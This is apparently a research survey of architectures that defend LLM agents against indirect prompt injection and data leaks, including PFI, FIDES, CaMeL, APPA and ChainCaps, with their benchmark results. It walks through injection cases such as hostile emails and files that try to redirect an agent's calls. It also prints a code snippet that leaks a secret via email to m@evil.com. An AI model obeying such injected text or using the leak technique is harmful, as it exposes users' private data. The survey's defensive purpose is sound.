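*System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) divides the agent into a planner, an executor and a security monitor. The planner is a language model that writes each step in a fixed format, naming the tool to call and its input. The executor is an ordinary program that carries out the step, and it can start a separate model for work such as summarising. The monitor labels every result as trusted or untrusted and shows the planner only the trusted ones. For each untrusted result, the planner gets a numbered reference, which it can use as input to a later step without seeing the contents.

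Labels combine as in Denning's model. The monitor can also label each item in a result separately, so if an inbox search returns two emails from colleagues and one from a stranger, the planner can read the colleagues' emails.

The paper proves that an attacker can't influence the plan. Take a request q and two situations, Q₁ and Q₂, that contain the same trusted information but differ in what strangers have written. Then for any sequence of steps π,

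Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂]

The hostile text doesn't make a harmful step more likely, but it can still change the data that the steps handle, for example by putting a false claim into a summary. On InjecAgent, no attack succeeded with any of four models, as expected from the proof when every tool result counts as untrusted.

This guarantee also rules out some tasks that users want done. If a user asks the agent to follow the installation guide on a website, the planner can't read the guide. PFI is designed to make such tasks possible.

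### Two agents with different permissions

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (Kim, Choi and Lee, 2025) splits the work between two agents. The privileged agent plans the task and can use every tool, but its context contains only trusted data. The unprivileged agent reads untrusted data and has no tools by default. Developers can give it harmless ones, such as web search, or access to public files.

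Each agent has its own access token, the credential that an online service checks before it allows an operation. A cloud drive can therefore refuse to show the unprivileged agent a private file, even if a hostile document causes that agent to request it. PFI also starts a new unprivileged agent for each job, so instructions from a web page can't stay in the agent's context and affect the next job.

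When a tool returns untrusted data, PFI stores it in a table and gives the privileged agent an identifier such as #DATA0. The agent can put this identifier into a later call, and PFI swaps in the real value just before the call runs.

### A web search sent by email

Suppose a user asks the agent to look up the date and location of a conference and send them to a colleague by email. Kim and colleagues work through a request like this:

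1. The privileged agent calls the search tool, which returns a web address and the text of the page. PFI stores both, and the agent sees only #DATA0 and #DATA1.
2. The agent needs two facts from the page. It sends #DATA1 to the unprivileged agent with a format for the reply, which has one text field for the date and one for the location.
3. The unprivileged agent receives the actual page text and fills in the two fields. PFI stores these values too and returns #DATA2 and #DATA3.
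4. The privileged agent writes the email with identifiers where the facts should go, and calls the mail tool.
5. PFI finds identifiers in the arguments. The unprivileged agent isn't allowed to send email, so PFI pauses the call and alerts the user.
6. If the user agrees, PFI replaces the identifiers with the real values and the email goes out.

If the page contains an order to forward the user's inbox, only the unprivileged agent reads it, and that agent has no mail tool. The order could end up in the date field, which accepts any text. But it would then be part of the email's contents, and the privileged agent would never read it.

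In another of the paper's examples, a user asks the agent to send Alice a summary of recent news, and the search returns an article with false stories and phishing links. The article contains no instructions to the agent, which does exactly what the user asked. The alert shows the text, the website it came from and the email field it is about to enter. The user spots the problem and refuses.

### When PFI interrupts the user

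PFI raises this kind of alert whenever untrusted data would enter an operation that the unprivileged agent couldn't perform itself. The agent's final answer counts as such an operation, so an agent that only reports what a website says also causes an alert.

PFI has a separate alert for instructions. If the user asks the agent to install a program by following an online guide, the privileged agent must explicitly request the guide as text to act on. PFI then prompts the user to decide whether to trust it. If the user agrees, the guide enters the privileged agent's context like any trusted text. f-secure has no equivalent of this endorsement step for text it labels untrusted.

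The alerts also name the sources of text that the unprivileged agent has rewritten, because PFI attaches every source in that agent's context to the result. This is a form of label creep, but the agent's small, fresh context limits it.

By default, PFI trusts no tool results from outside. Tool developers can mark certain results as trusted, and when an alert appears, users can choose whether to trust the source once, always or never.

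### The comparison with GPT-4o

Kim and colleagues tested PFI on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and on 19 shell-command tasks based on the AgentBench benchmark. They tried both prompt injection and what they call data injection, in which the attacker supplies false information or a phishing link without giving the agent an order. They normally count data injection as successful if the agent uses the attacker's data in a privileged operation.

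The table gives the results with GPT-4o. A task counts as attacked if at least one attack on it succeeded, and as completed securely if the agent finished it and no attack succeeded.

| Benchmark | System | Tasks attacked | Completed securely | Alerts per task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | No defence | 81.44% | 12.37% | 0 |
| AgentDojo | IsolateGPT | 72.16% | About 10% | 0.04 |
| AgentDojo | f-secure | Not given | 40.21% | Not given |
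| AgentDojo | PFI | 0% | 61.86% | 1.49 |
| AgentDojo | Alert on every call | 0% | Not given | 4.11 |
| Shell tasks | No defence | 100% | 0% | 0 |
| Shell tasks | IsolateGPT | 84.21% | About 10% | 0.26 |
| Shell tasks | f-secure | Not given | 10.53% | Not given |
| Shell tasks | PFI | 0% | 68.42% | 1.05 |
| Shell tasks | Alert on every call | 0% | Not given | 1.84 |

The percentages of tasks successfully attacked are much higher than ordinary attack success rates because each AgentDojo task faced several attacks. Without a defence, 39.41% of the individual prompt injections succeeded, but at least one succeeded in 73.20% of the tasks.

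PFI also made the agent less capable. The undefended agent completed 81.44% of the AgentDojo tasks if one ignores the attacks, about 20 percentage points more than PFI. Kim and colleagues examined 108 tasks that the undefended agent had completed and PFI had not. In more than half of them, the privileged agent used an identifier incorrectly, and in another fifth it asked the unprivileged agent a badly formed question. The researchers suggest training models to work with identifiers, which could help PFI complete some of these tasks.

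On AgentDojo, PFI increased the average time per task from 5.5 to 8.9 seconds and used 91% more tokens. The shell tasks took about three times as long with PFI and used 3.5 times as many tokens. The privileged agent often couldn't tell why a request to the unprivileged agent had failed, so it kept trying other commands.

### Why isolation by app stopped so few attacks

IsolateGPT's hub warns about contact with an app outside its plan, but many of AgentDojo's attacks stay inside one app. For instance, an attacker can send the user a small payment whose subject line contains an instruction to transfer money. The agent reads the instruction through the banking app when it checks recent transactions, and the transfer would use the same app. No message passes through the hub, so IsolateGPT gives no warning.

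Other attacks use two apps that the plan already connects. In the news example, the user asked for web text in an email, so the plan already has the web app supplying text to the mail app. A phishing link in that text doesn't deviate from the plan, which leaves the hub no basis for flagging it.

Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao had already attacked IsolateGPT, then called SecGPT, using actions that were part of the agent's plan. In one attack, the user asks the agent to read emails about budgets and notify a manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. A stranger's email tells the agent to send all the budgets to another address. Reading and sending mail are both in the plan, so SecGPT treats the request as harmless and the user authorises it. In the other, the agent has to delete one file after emailing it, and text inside that file makes it delete everything in the folder. f-secure stopped both attacks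 because its planner never read the hostile text.

The shell tasks suit IsolateGPT even less because they all use a single shell tool, so a boundary between apps has almost nothing to separate. PFI can draw a boundary inside a single tool because it gives the privileged agent a normal shell and the unprivileged agent a sandboxed one.

### How far the comparison can be trusted

Kim and colleagues tested their own version of IsolateGPT rather than the original. Their version groups related tools into apps and raises an alert when an agent contacts an app outside the plan. The original also asks users for consent before apps exchange messages and before irreversible actions. The rebuilt version raised only four alerts over the 97 AgentDojo tasks, so it probably left out these consent requests. Including them would have given users more chances to stop an attack, but it would also have interrupted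 them far more often.

The test counted an attack as blocked whenever the system warned the user, so PFI's 0% assumes that users refuse every harmful request. Its completion rate assumes that they also approve the alerts that a legitimate task needs. Real users would have to tell the two apart, and in the experiments on permission requests described earlier, people often approved actions they should have refused. PFI's alerts show more information than most of the requests in those experiments, but none of PFI's tests involved users.

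Kim and colleagues report that PFI raises no false alarms, in the sense that every alert involves untrusted data entering a privileged operation. An email with an accurate news summary causes the same alert as one with a phishing link. The 144 alerts on AgentDojo, spread over 97 tasks, therefore mostly measure how often ordinary work uses outside data.

Kim and colleagues also rebuilt f-secure, by switching off PFI's alerts and its way of endorsing instructions. On AgentDojo, this reduced secure completions from 61.86% to 40.21%, which is still far above IsolateGPT. Much of PFI's advantage on AgentDojo therefore comes from hiding untrusted data from the planner, which requires no help from the user. On the shell tasks, the reduced version securely completed only two of 19, so PFI depends almost entirely on the features that require the user's judgment for those tasks.

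Kim and colleagues also changed the benchmarks. They altered ten of AgentDojo's user tasks to rely on untrusted data and added 97 data injections. They also wrote 14 of the 19 shell tasks, using ChatGPT to generate candidates. These changes were reasonable, since the original benchmarks don't cover all the attacks that PFI is meant to stop. But IsolateGPT's designers had explicitly excluded attacks within one app, and IsolateGPT doesn't check whether planted data is true. Its low score shows that its protection is narrow, but doesn't contradict its results against attacks from one app on another.

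The trust policy affects the scores too. For 75 tools, Kim and colleagues decided by hand which results to trust and what the unprivileged agent could access. The trusted sources include every email from the user's company, all websites ending in .gov or .edu, and a travel company's promotional address. They chose some of these so that the tests would mix trusted and untrusted data. A stricter list would have caused more alerts. An attacker who took over a coworker's email account would bypass PFI's protection, because the privileged agent would read emails from that account directly.

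### Newer models and an independent test

All four models in the PFI tests date from 2024, and newer ones resist AgentDojo's standard prompt injections much better. *aiAuthZ* (2026), a paper on authorising agents' calls, reports that none of these attacks succeeded against two undefended current models, although it tried only 20 cases per model. In Ma and colleagues' AutoDojo tests, the same kind of attack succeeded less than 10% of the time against an undefended DeepSeek-v4-Pro. The attack success rates for IsolateGPT and the undefended agent would probably be far lower with today's models.

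Data injection may not decline as quickly, because the model can follow the user's request faithfully and still pass on bad data. In the original tests, prompt injection succeeded against Claude 3.5 Sonnet in 12.37% of AgentDojo tasks, while data injection succeeded in 38.14%. In a follow-up, *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) found that untrusted data disguised as trusted data could still get past defences that stopped nearly all injected instructions.

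The best independent evidence on PFI comes from *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026), which presents a rival system. It measured how often PFI completed the 60 open-ended tasks in AgentDyn when no attack was present.

| Model | Completed without a defence | Completed with PFI | Attacks that succeeded without a defence | Attacks that succeeded with PFI |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 46.7% | 15.0% | 49.6% | 3.4% |
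| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 10.0% | 37.4% | 1.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 36.7% | 5.0% | 50.8% | 0% |
| Qwen3-235B | 65.0% | 8.3% | 61.8% | 7.1% |

PFI still stopped most attacks, though fewer than in its developers' tests. When an attacking model revised its injections against PFI, more than 10% succeeded with Qwen3-235B. PFI reduced task completion much more on AgentDyn than on AgentDojo, because AgentDyn's tasks often require the agent to act on something it finds in an email or file.

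The ROPE paper gives three examples of what went wrong, including these two. In one, the user asks the agent to follow instructions in an email John has just sent. PFI hides the sender as well as the text, so the agent reports that it can't find an email from John. In another, the user asks the agent to send a document summary to Lily, but the agent picks the wrong identifier and sends the summary to the user's own address.

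The remaining example is more worrying because hiding data from the planner creates a new way to leak data. The user asks the agent to send some SSH keys to Alice Miller, whose address is in the inbox. The agent can't read the address, so it invents one and sends the keys there. PFI checks for untrusted data in a call, and an invented address contains none, so the check doesn't flag the recipient.

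A policy that trusted John's and Alice's addresses would have let the agent read their emails, so some of these failures depend on the settings as much as on the design. The ROPE tests didn't include IsolateGPT, so they don't repeat the direct comparison with it.

### The salary report under PFI

PFI doesn't label data as secret, and Kim and colleagues' policy treats the user's private files as trusted, so the privileged agent could read the salary spreadsheet and email the figures to anyone without triggering an alert. In one of their examples, the agent sends Alice a schedule from the user's private calendar, and PFI correctly raises no alert because no untrusted data is involved.

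The industry benchmarks would cause an alert because they come from the web. However, the alert would be about whether the user trusts the benchmark figures, and a user who does would approve the email with the salaries in it. The privileged agent also can't read the benchmarks to compare them with the company's pay. The simplest solution would be to mark the benchmark site as trusted, but then the whole report would go out without an alert.

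## FIDES and CaMeL: following data from call to call

PFI would miss the salary leak because its labels record only how trustworthy data is. FIDES and CaMeL, two systems from 2025, also record who may read each piece of data, so they can check this before a call sends the data. FIDES adds labels to an ordinary agent that chooses one call at a time. In CaMeL, the model writes a program for the whole task, and an interpreter tracks every value in it.

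### Labels and checks in FIDES

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe FIDES, which they built at Microsoft. Each label has two parts. One marks the data as trusted or untrusted. The other says how secret it is, either with a simple public or secret mark or with a list of the people who may read it. Labels combine as in Denning's model, and only people who could read both pieces of data may read the result. For trust levels t and sets of readers R,

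(t₁, R₁) ⊕ (t₂, R₂) = (t₁ ⊕ t₂, R₁ ∩ R₂)

In the salary report, the spreadsheet might be trusted and readable only by the finance team, while the benchmarks page is untrusted and readable by anyone. A summary of both is then untrusted, and only the finance team may read it.

Small programs wrapped around the tools attach the labels. They can label each field of a result separately, so the date of an email may be trusted even though its text isn't. FIDES cautiously gives a model's output the combined label of everything in the context.

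Before each call, FIDES checks the labels against the policy for that tool. Costa and colleagues build their policies from two rules. The trust rule allows a call only if nothing untrusted influenced the decision to make it, and a policy can extend this to particular arguments, such as the recipient of a message. The reader rule allows a call only if everyone who would receive the data is permitted to read it.

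### A two-call task in FIDES

With these rules alone, an agent that read one untrusted email could do very little afterwards. FIDES therefore hides some values from the planning model, much as PFI does, and shows it a variable name instead. FIDES hides a value only when showing that value would make the context's label more restrictive.

Suppose a user asks the agent to summarise the top three emails in the inbox and send the summary to a colleague on Slack. FIDES handles the task like this:

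1. The planner calls the email tool. The emails are untrusted and the context so far is trusted, so FIDES stores them and shows the planner only the name #read_emails_0.
2. The planner asks a separate model, which has no tools, to summarise #read_emails_0. FIDES stores the answer as #query_llm_0, with the combined label of the context and the emails.
3. The planner calls the Slack tool, with the colleague's name as the recipient and #query_llm_0 as the message.
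4. FIDES checks the call. The planner has seen nothing untrusted, so the call passes the trust rule. If the policy also includes the reader rule, the colleague must be allowed to read all three emails.
5. FIDES replaces the variable name with the summary and sends the message.

A hostile email could make the summary false or empty, but it couldn't change the recipient or add another call.

Some tasks require the planner to know what a hidden value contains. It can open the variable, but the context then takes on the contents' label. A more limited option is to ask the separate model a yes-or-no question, such as whether an email requests a meeting, and reveal only the answer. A policy may allow this because an attacker can influence only one bit. Costa and colleagues did not test this option.

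Whether FIDES would block the salary report depends on how the company combines the two rules. If both the spreadsheet and the web page stay hidden, the planner's decision to send the email is trusted. Costa and colleagues suggest that when a trusted decision breaks the reader rule, one can assume the user intended it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a later paper from Microsoft, lets tools that send data out run if the call passes either rule. The salary email would go out under that policy, because the agent made an ordinary mistake with no attacker involved. A policy that requires both rules would block it.

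### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. By their own count, 152 attacks succeeded against an undefended agent, 21 against FIDES with its policy checks off, and none with the checks on. AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successes with the checks on. The researchers discounted these after reading the logs, partly because their policies allow some actions that the benchmark counts as attacks, such as sending a Slack message without a link.

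The labels in this test were also unusually accurate, because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in AgentDojo uses it. A real operator has no list of attacks to work from and would have to guess which fields an attacker might control.

The next table gives the share of tasks completed when there is no attack. The middle column is for an agent that has labels and policy checks but can't hide values.

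| Environment | No defence | Labels and checks, nothing hidden | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

The middle column measures label creep fairly directly. On Slack, a single untrusted message often blocked the rest of the task, and completion fell from 93.3% to 20.0%. Hiding values recovered some of this loss everywhere except in the travel tasks. The policies let most travel tools run after the agent had read untrusted data, so hiding values helped little there, and GPT-4o often handled the variables badly.

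FIDES lost fewer tasks to its security restrictions when it used a better model. With OpenAI's o1, it completed 68% of the travel tasks, and on average it completed about 16 percentage points more tasks than the agent that hides nothing. With GPT-4o, the difference was 8 points.

Some failures have little to do with the model. More than 40% of the banking and Slack tasks require the agent to choose its next step based on what it reads, compared with 5% to 10% in the other two environments. Many banking tasks tell it to read a file and follow the instructions there, which the policies forbid. The agent could have avoided other failures. In one Slack task, it looked up the list of channels even though the user had named the channel, and reading that list made its context untrusted.

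### A program with labelled values in CaMeL

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced Google DeepMind's CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) and *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) explain its design and extend it.

A privileged model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. This model never sees the results of the tool calls. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads untrusted text when the program needs information from it. The interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. It also records where each value came from, which other values went into it and who may read it.

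Nikolaou and colleagues give a short example with two tool calls and one question to the quarantined model, lightly simplified here:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

Suppose an attacker has posted a message in the channel that gives a false address for Bob.

1. The interpreter reads the channel and records that `messages` came from an untrusted source.
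2. The quarantined model finds the false address. The interpreter stores it as `email` and records that it depends on `messages`.
3. Before it sends anything, the interpreter runs the policy for the messaging tool. The policy is a short Python function that receives the arguments with their records, then allows or denies the call.
4. If the policy requires a trusted recipient, it denies the call.

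The attacker couldn't add a call, because the program was finished before any model read the channel. But without the policy, the program would have sent the message to the wrong person. The policy would also reject Bob's real address if it came from the channel. CaMeL can ask the user to confirm such a call, according to *PolicySniff* (2026), a paper on a different kind of leak.

CaMeL handles the salary report more precisely than ACE. The summary depends on the spreadsheet, so only the finance team may read it. A policy can block the email to the distribution list and still allow one to the finance director, whereas ACE gives the whole mail app a single clearance. If the program also produced a separate summary of the benchmarks, that summary would stay public. This works only if someone has recorded who may read the spreadsheet.

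Like ACE, CaMeL can branch on a result only by choosing among steps that the model wrote in advance. FIDES can open a variable partway through a task and plan again, but doing so makes its context more restrictive.

### CaMeL in 2026 tests

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that two injections were counted as successful against CaMeL in its original AgentDojo tests. In one, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's payment instructions, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. CaMeL's designers exclude such cases. The other was a scoring error, in which the agent quoted hotel reviews containing the text the benchmark checks for. Kolluri and colleagues put the loss of completed tasks in the original FIDES and CaMeL tests at up to 30%.

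Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With its policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed half as many tasks as with them off. Without the policies, 138 of 141 attacks in one group succeeded with the model MiMo-v2.5. In two further cases, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely, and the privileged model wrote a program with a branch for every tool, which could carry out whatever the file said. The attacker could then choose the calls through the file, even though the program never changed.

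*Can CaMeLs Talk?*, which Shumailov also worked on, tested five models on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded with no defence and 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL without policies. But almost all of the improvement came from GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. Without CaMeL, no attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 and only 1.5% succeeded against Claude Fable 5, so AgentDojo's standard attacks can hardly test a defence on such models.

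CaMeL also reduces task completion less with newer models. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, it lowered completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Most failures occurred because the agent discovered partway through that it needed a step the program didn't contain.

*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) tested harder attacks on a current model, GPT-5.6 Luna. The model resisted all 40 ordinary AgentDojo attacks, so the researchers rewrote them. Each new attack stayed on the user's topic, applied only under some condition, and changed the content of a call or answer but not the choice of tools. Seven of these (17.5%) succeeded without a defence and one (2.5%) succeeded with CaMeL, too few to estimate the rates precisely. Under these attacks, CaMeL completed 27.5% of the user's tasks, while PromptArmor, which uses a language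 model to remove suspicious instructions, completed 90% and let three attacks through. PromptArmor offers no guarantee against an attacker who learns how to evade it, but many users would accept two more successful attacks in exchange for about three times as many completed tasks.

### Flows that the labels miss

Both systems can miss Denning's implicit flows, which leak information through the agent's choices. Costa and colleagues chose not to track these flows in FIDES, judging that preventing them would rule out almost any public action after the agent had read something secret.

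CaMeL does more here. *PolicySniff* reports that its designers examined leaks through conditional requests to outside sites, through errors that change later steps, and through timing. A strict mode labels whatever happens inside a branch with the label of the condition, and CaMeL's programs have no access to a clock. Garby and colleagues nevertheless found a gap, based on an example from the 1970s. A program like this one shows how it works:

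```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and is marked secret. The fourth line then doesn't change `rich`, so CaMeL never marks `rich` as secret and lets the email through. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold. CaMeL can also rerun a program after a refusal. Whether it refuses may depend on a secret, so repeated attempts could reveal the secret one bit at a time.

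An attacker would struggle to use these gaps, because the privileged model writes the program from the user's request alone and has no reason to write the code above. The gaps matter more if the model itself is untrustworthy, or if a company wants a proof that nothing leaks. *PolicySniff* describes a leak that labels can't address. A program that shares a graphics processor with the agent's model can infer which policy the model is processing by timing its own work, much like Lampson's signal through a slowdown.

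Wrong labels and policies are probably a more common danger. FIDES's tests treated an email's sender and recipients as its only readers, though someone may have shared it more widely. CaMeL applies its policies to one call at a time, so they can't naturally express a rule such as "close every ticket you open". Nikolaou and colleagues add a check of the whole program before it runs, which can enforce such rules and avoids running a task that would fail at its last step.

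### Labels lost between agents

Peters-Gill and colleagues show that when agents each have their own tools, running CaMeL in every agent doesn't make the whole system secure. In their example, one agent reads a database of job applicants, another sends notifications, and an orchestrator directs both. The user asks the system to send Julie a summary of the applicants on Slack, but an attacker has put an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

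The orchestrator's program receives the summary as an untrusted value and never shows it to the orchestrator's privileged model. But the program inserts the summary into a sentence, "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", and passes it to the notification agent, which treats the whole sentence as its user's request. That agent's privileged model reads the attacker's instruction and writes a program that sends both the Slack message and the email. Every attack that still succeeded against CaMeL in their tests worked this way.

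Their remedy splits each message between agents into an instruction, which must not depend on any tool result, and labeled data, which the receiving agent's privileged model can't read. No attack in the benchmark succeeded against this version. On the maintenance tasks, it reduced completion by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models.

### A simulation of agent networks

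Dividing work among agents can also limit label creep, because each agent has its own context and picks up only the labels of the data it handles. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated how much this helps, without using a language model. Their program generated 1,000 random tasks of 20 tool calls each, assigned the calls to five agents and followed the labels through ten million runs for each way of connecting the agents.

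An agent gets a "sensitive" label when it makes certain calls or when it receives or forwards sensitive data, and it keeps the label for the rest of the task. The researchers measured lost utility as the share of calls that add the label or are made by an agent that already has it. They compared each layout with an ideal one, in which agents that need each other's results are linked directly.

In the main comparison, the number of sensitive calls ranged from four to all 20. At four, a hub layout lost roughly 5 percentage points more than the ideal, a hierarchy about 4 and a ring about 3, while a network linking every pair of agents matched the ideal. The hub does badly because it forwards everything, so once it has carried one sensitive result, its label spreads to the agents it contacts afterwards.

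Across nine layouts, networks with a higher density, the share of possible direct links that exist, almost always lost less utility. The rank correlation was −0.96, which doesn't measure how much less they lost. Denser networks also need more monitoring, because someone has to monitor every link. Five fully connected agents have 10 links, and 20 have 190.

Gregory and colleagues then gave the sensitive tools to particular agents, as a company might with a dedicated banking agent, instead of spreading them at random. This reduced lost utility in every layout, but the ideal layout benefited most, so the gap between it and layouts such as the hub grew. Even the ideal layout lost some utility, and the researchers conclude that a system also needs some way to relax labels.

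The simulation probably overstates the problem for systems like FIDES. It counts every call made under a sensitive label as a loss, even one that no policy would block, and its agents can't pass on data without taking on the data's label. A real model might also do its public work first and read the sensitive files last. The ranking of the layouts is therefore more credible than the percentages, and neither measures how many tasks a real agent would finish.

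The results suggest how to combine isolation with flow tracking. IsolateGPT's hub stores conversations with every app. If a company added labels to IsolateGPT, that shared memory would soon become sensitive and could restrict every app that used it. A hub that only forwarded labelled messages, without reading or storing them, would behave more like a set of direct links. The company in the salary example could then give the payroll files to one agent and routine email to another. The mail agent could keep sending meeting times, and the summary would reach it with a label that a policy could check before the agent sent it out.

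### Continuing after a refusal

When a policy blocks the salary email, the user may still want to send some version of it. The user can approve that one call or endorse the data it depends on, and the choice affects how often the agent has to ask. In an example from Kolluri and colleagues, an untrusted but harmless email lists ten to-do items, each of which requires a restricted call. Approving the calls one by one takes ten decisions. If the user endorses the email instead, FIDES treats it as trusted, and the agent can do all ten tasks after one decision.

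Kolluri and colleagues built an agent on top of FIDES that knows the labels and policies and can ask for either. On AgentDojo, it completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES without human help, and cut the number of human decisions by a factor of up to 1.9. They also argue that the usual comparisons are unfair to flow tracking, because an undefended agent in a benchmark acts freely, whereas a commercial one often asks for approval before doing anything important.

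Endorsement removes protection, though. Two of 1,296 attempted attacks on Garby and colleagues' own agent succeeded, both because its plan had endorsed untrusted data. Kolluri and colleagues' agent can't relax secrecy labels this way. They think the decision to release private data depends too much on the situation, so users have to approve each call that would release it.

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system designed around what happens after a refusal. The system labels data much as FIDES does, but before a call it also adds the label of whatever the call is expected to read. This matters for a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it in one step, because the agent's context is still public when the call begins. APPA then checks the actual result before the model sees it.

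If APPA blocks a call, it works out which of the permitted remedies would help and reports them to the agent. For the salary report, these might include:

- Approval of this one email. A person, a fixed rule or another model reviews the exact text and recipients. The approval doesn't change any labels, so the agent can't use it for a second email.
- An approved transformation. A program that the company trusts removes the pay figures, and the result gets a less restrictive label.
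- A temporary branch. A copy of the agent reads the sensitive or untrusted data, returns a short answer in a fixed format and disappears. The main agent's context keeps its old label if the company's policy accepts the answer at that level.

The agent has to choose a branch before it reads the spreadsheet, because a branch can't remove a label already on the context. The fixed format allows numbers within set limits or choices from a list, but no free text. Like the narrow types in IsolateGPT, this format keeps injected instructions out but can still let through a false answer or a salary. The company therefore has to decide explicitly whether the answer may become public. Adding a missing earlier step, such as a required review, may resolve other blocked calls.

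Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with three 2026 models, including GPT-5.6 Luna. They used a public benchmark, AgentThreatBench, and their own Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office tasks. They skipped AgentDojo because current models resist its attacks and its tasks usually end soon after the risky step. In half the runs, the prompt encouraged the model to follow instructions it found in data. The ranges in the table cover all three models and, for FIDES, two configurations.

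| Benchmark and prompt | Tasks completed, APPA | Attacks succeeded, APPA | Tasks completed, FIDES | Attacks succeeded, FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentThreatBench, normal | 64–76% | 0% | 27–73% | 0–3% |
| AgentThreatBench, encouraged | 69–77% | 0% | 24–74% | 5–31% |
| Bench-Corp, normal | 87–90% | 0% | 36–46% | 27–35% |
| Bench-Corp, encouraged | 89–91% | 0% | 36–45% | 26–35% |

The comparison with FIDES is weak evidence about flow tracking in general, because Kravchenko and colleagues wrote the FIDES policies themselves, and these omit several rules that Bench-Corp tests, such as exact recipients and the order of steps. Comparing versions of APPA is more informative. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the full version completed 88% of the Bench-Corp tasks, compared with 35% without its suggested remedies and 56.5% without temporary branches. No attack succeeded against any of these versions.

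A tired user may grant these approvals carelessly, as with IsolateGPT's dialogs, and Kravchenko and colleagues leave approval fatigue for future work. APPA limits the damage from a careless click to one exact call. But for the salary report, that call is the leak, so whoever reviews the email still has to notice the pay figures in it.

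## ChainCaps: per-function isolation and flow tracking compared on the same traces

FIDES, CaMeL and APPA can label data with the people who may read it. ChainCaps, which Jiang and colleagues presented in May 2026 along with the salary report, instead records which sinks each piece of data may still reach. They compared ChainCaps with per-function isolation and with simpler labels on recordings of the same agent runs. Isolation blocked far fewer attacks than either kind of flow tracking. But the researchers wrote the tasks themselves and used simplified models of the competing defences.

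### Budgets of permitted sinks

ChainCaps is a proxy that relays messages between an agent and its MCP servers, and it requires no changes to the model or the servers. It gives every value, such as a tool result, a budget, which is the set of sink privileges the value still has. Each privilege combines an operation with a scope, such as sending email to company addresses or writing files in one folder. Wider privileges include narrower ones, so data that may go to anyone at the company may also go to the finance director.

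A manifest for each tool lists the sinks the tool can use and the starting budgets of the data it reads. It also sets a limit, Pass(t), on the budget of anything that tool t produces. When the tool turns inputs x₁ to xₖ into an output y, the proxy applies the transfer rule:

B(y) = Pass(t) ∩ B(x₁) ∩ … ∩ B(xₖ)

The intersection (∩) keeps only the privileges that all the sets share, so the output can lose privileges along the way but can't gain any.

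Before a call to tool t with arguments a, the proxy works out which privilege the call requires, written Req(t, a). For an email, this depends on the recipients. Under the sink rule, the call goes ahead only if

Req(t, a) ∈ B(x) for every value x that contributed to a

Like FIDES, the proxy treats everything in the context as a possible influence on what the model writes, so it also keeps a budget for the whole context. This budget shrinks when a result with fewer privileges arrives, and it limits every later call. A call that fails the check can still go ahead with a signed, single-use token that releases the data for one exact request.

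Budgets are a kind of label, but they combine by intersection instead of Denning's ⊕. ChainCaps is therefore also a flow-tracking system, although its labels describe where data may go rather than how secret it is.

### The salary report as a calculation

Suppose the company allows the agent to show salary data to the user and to email it to the finance team. The benchmarks are public, and the summariser's own limit allows everything. The summary's budget is then the intersection of the other two:

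| Data | Budget |
|---|---|
| Salary spreadsheet | Show to the user, email to the finance team |
| Benchmarks page | Show to the user, email to anyone, send to any website |
| Summary of both | Show to the user, email to the finance team |

Emailing the summary to the distribution list requires a privilege that the summary doesn't have, so the proxy blocks the email. The same summary could still go to the finance director or appear on the user's screen. In Jiang and colleagues' stricter version, the agent may only display the salaries.

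The context budget causes label creep here. Once the agent has read the spreadsheet, even a summary of only the benchmarks is restricted to the finance team.

ChainCaps can reset the context budget when a new task begins. On a set of difficult but harmless scenarios, this reduced false alarms from 45% to 20%. The reset is safe only if text from the earlier task is also removed from the model's context. Otherwise, the model could still copy a salary from that text into a later email.

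### The non-amplification theorem

Jiang and colleagues prove that a chain of calls can't give data a privilege that it lacked at the start. Let O(a) be the set of sources that contributed to the arguments a, either directly or through other tools, and let Init(o) be the starting budget of data from source o. If ChainCaps allows a call without a release token, then

Req(t, a) ∈ Init(o) for every source o in O(a)

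The proof follows the data from source to sink. A value starts with its source's budget, and every step either keeps that budget or removes privileges from it, so if the required privilege is still present at the sink, it must have been in the source's budget. Denning's observation that a sequence of secure operations is itself secure rests on much the same reasoning.

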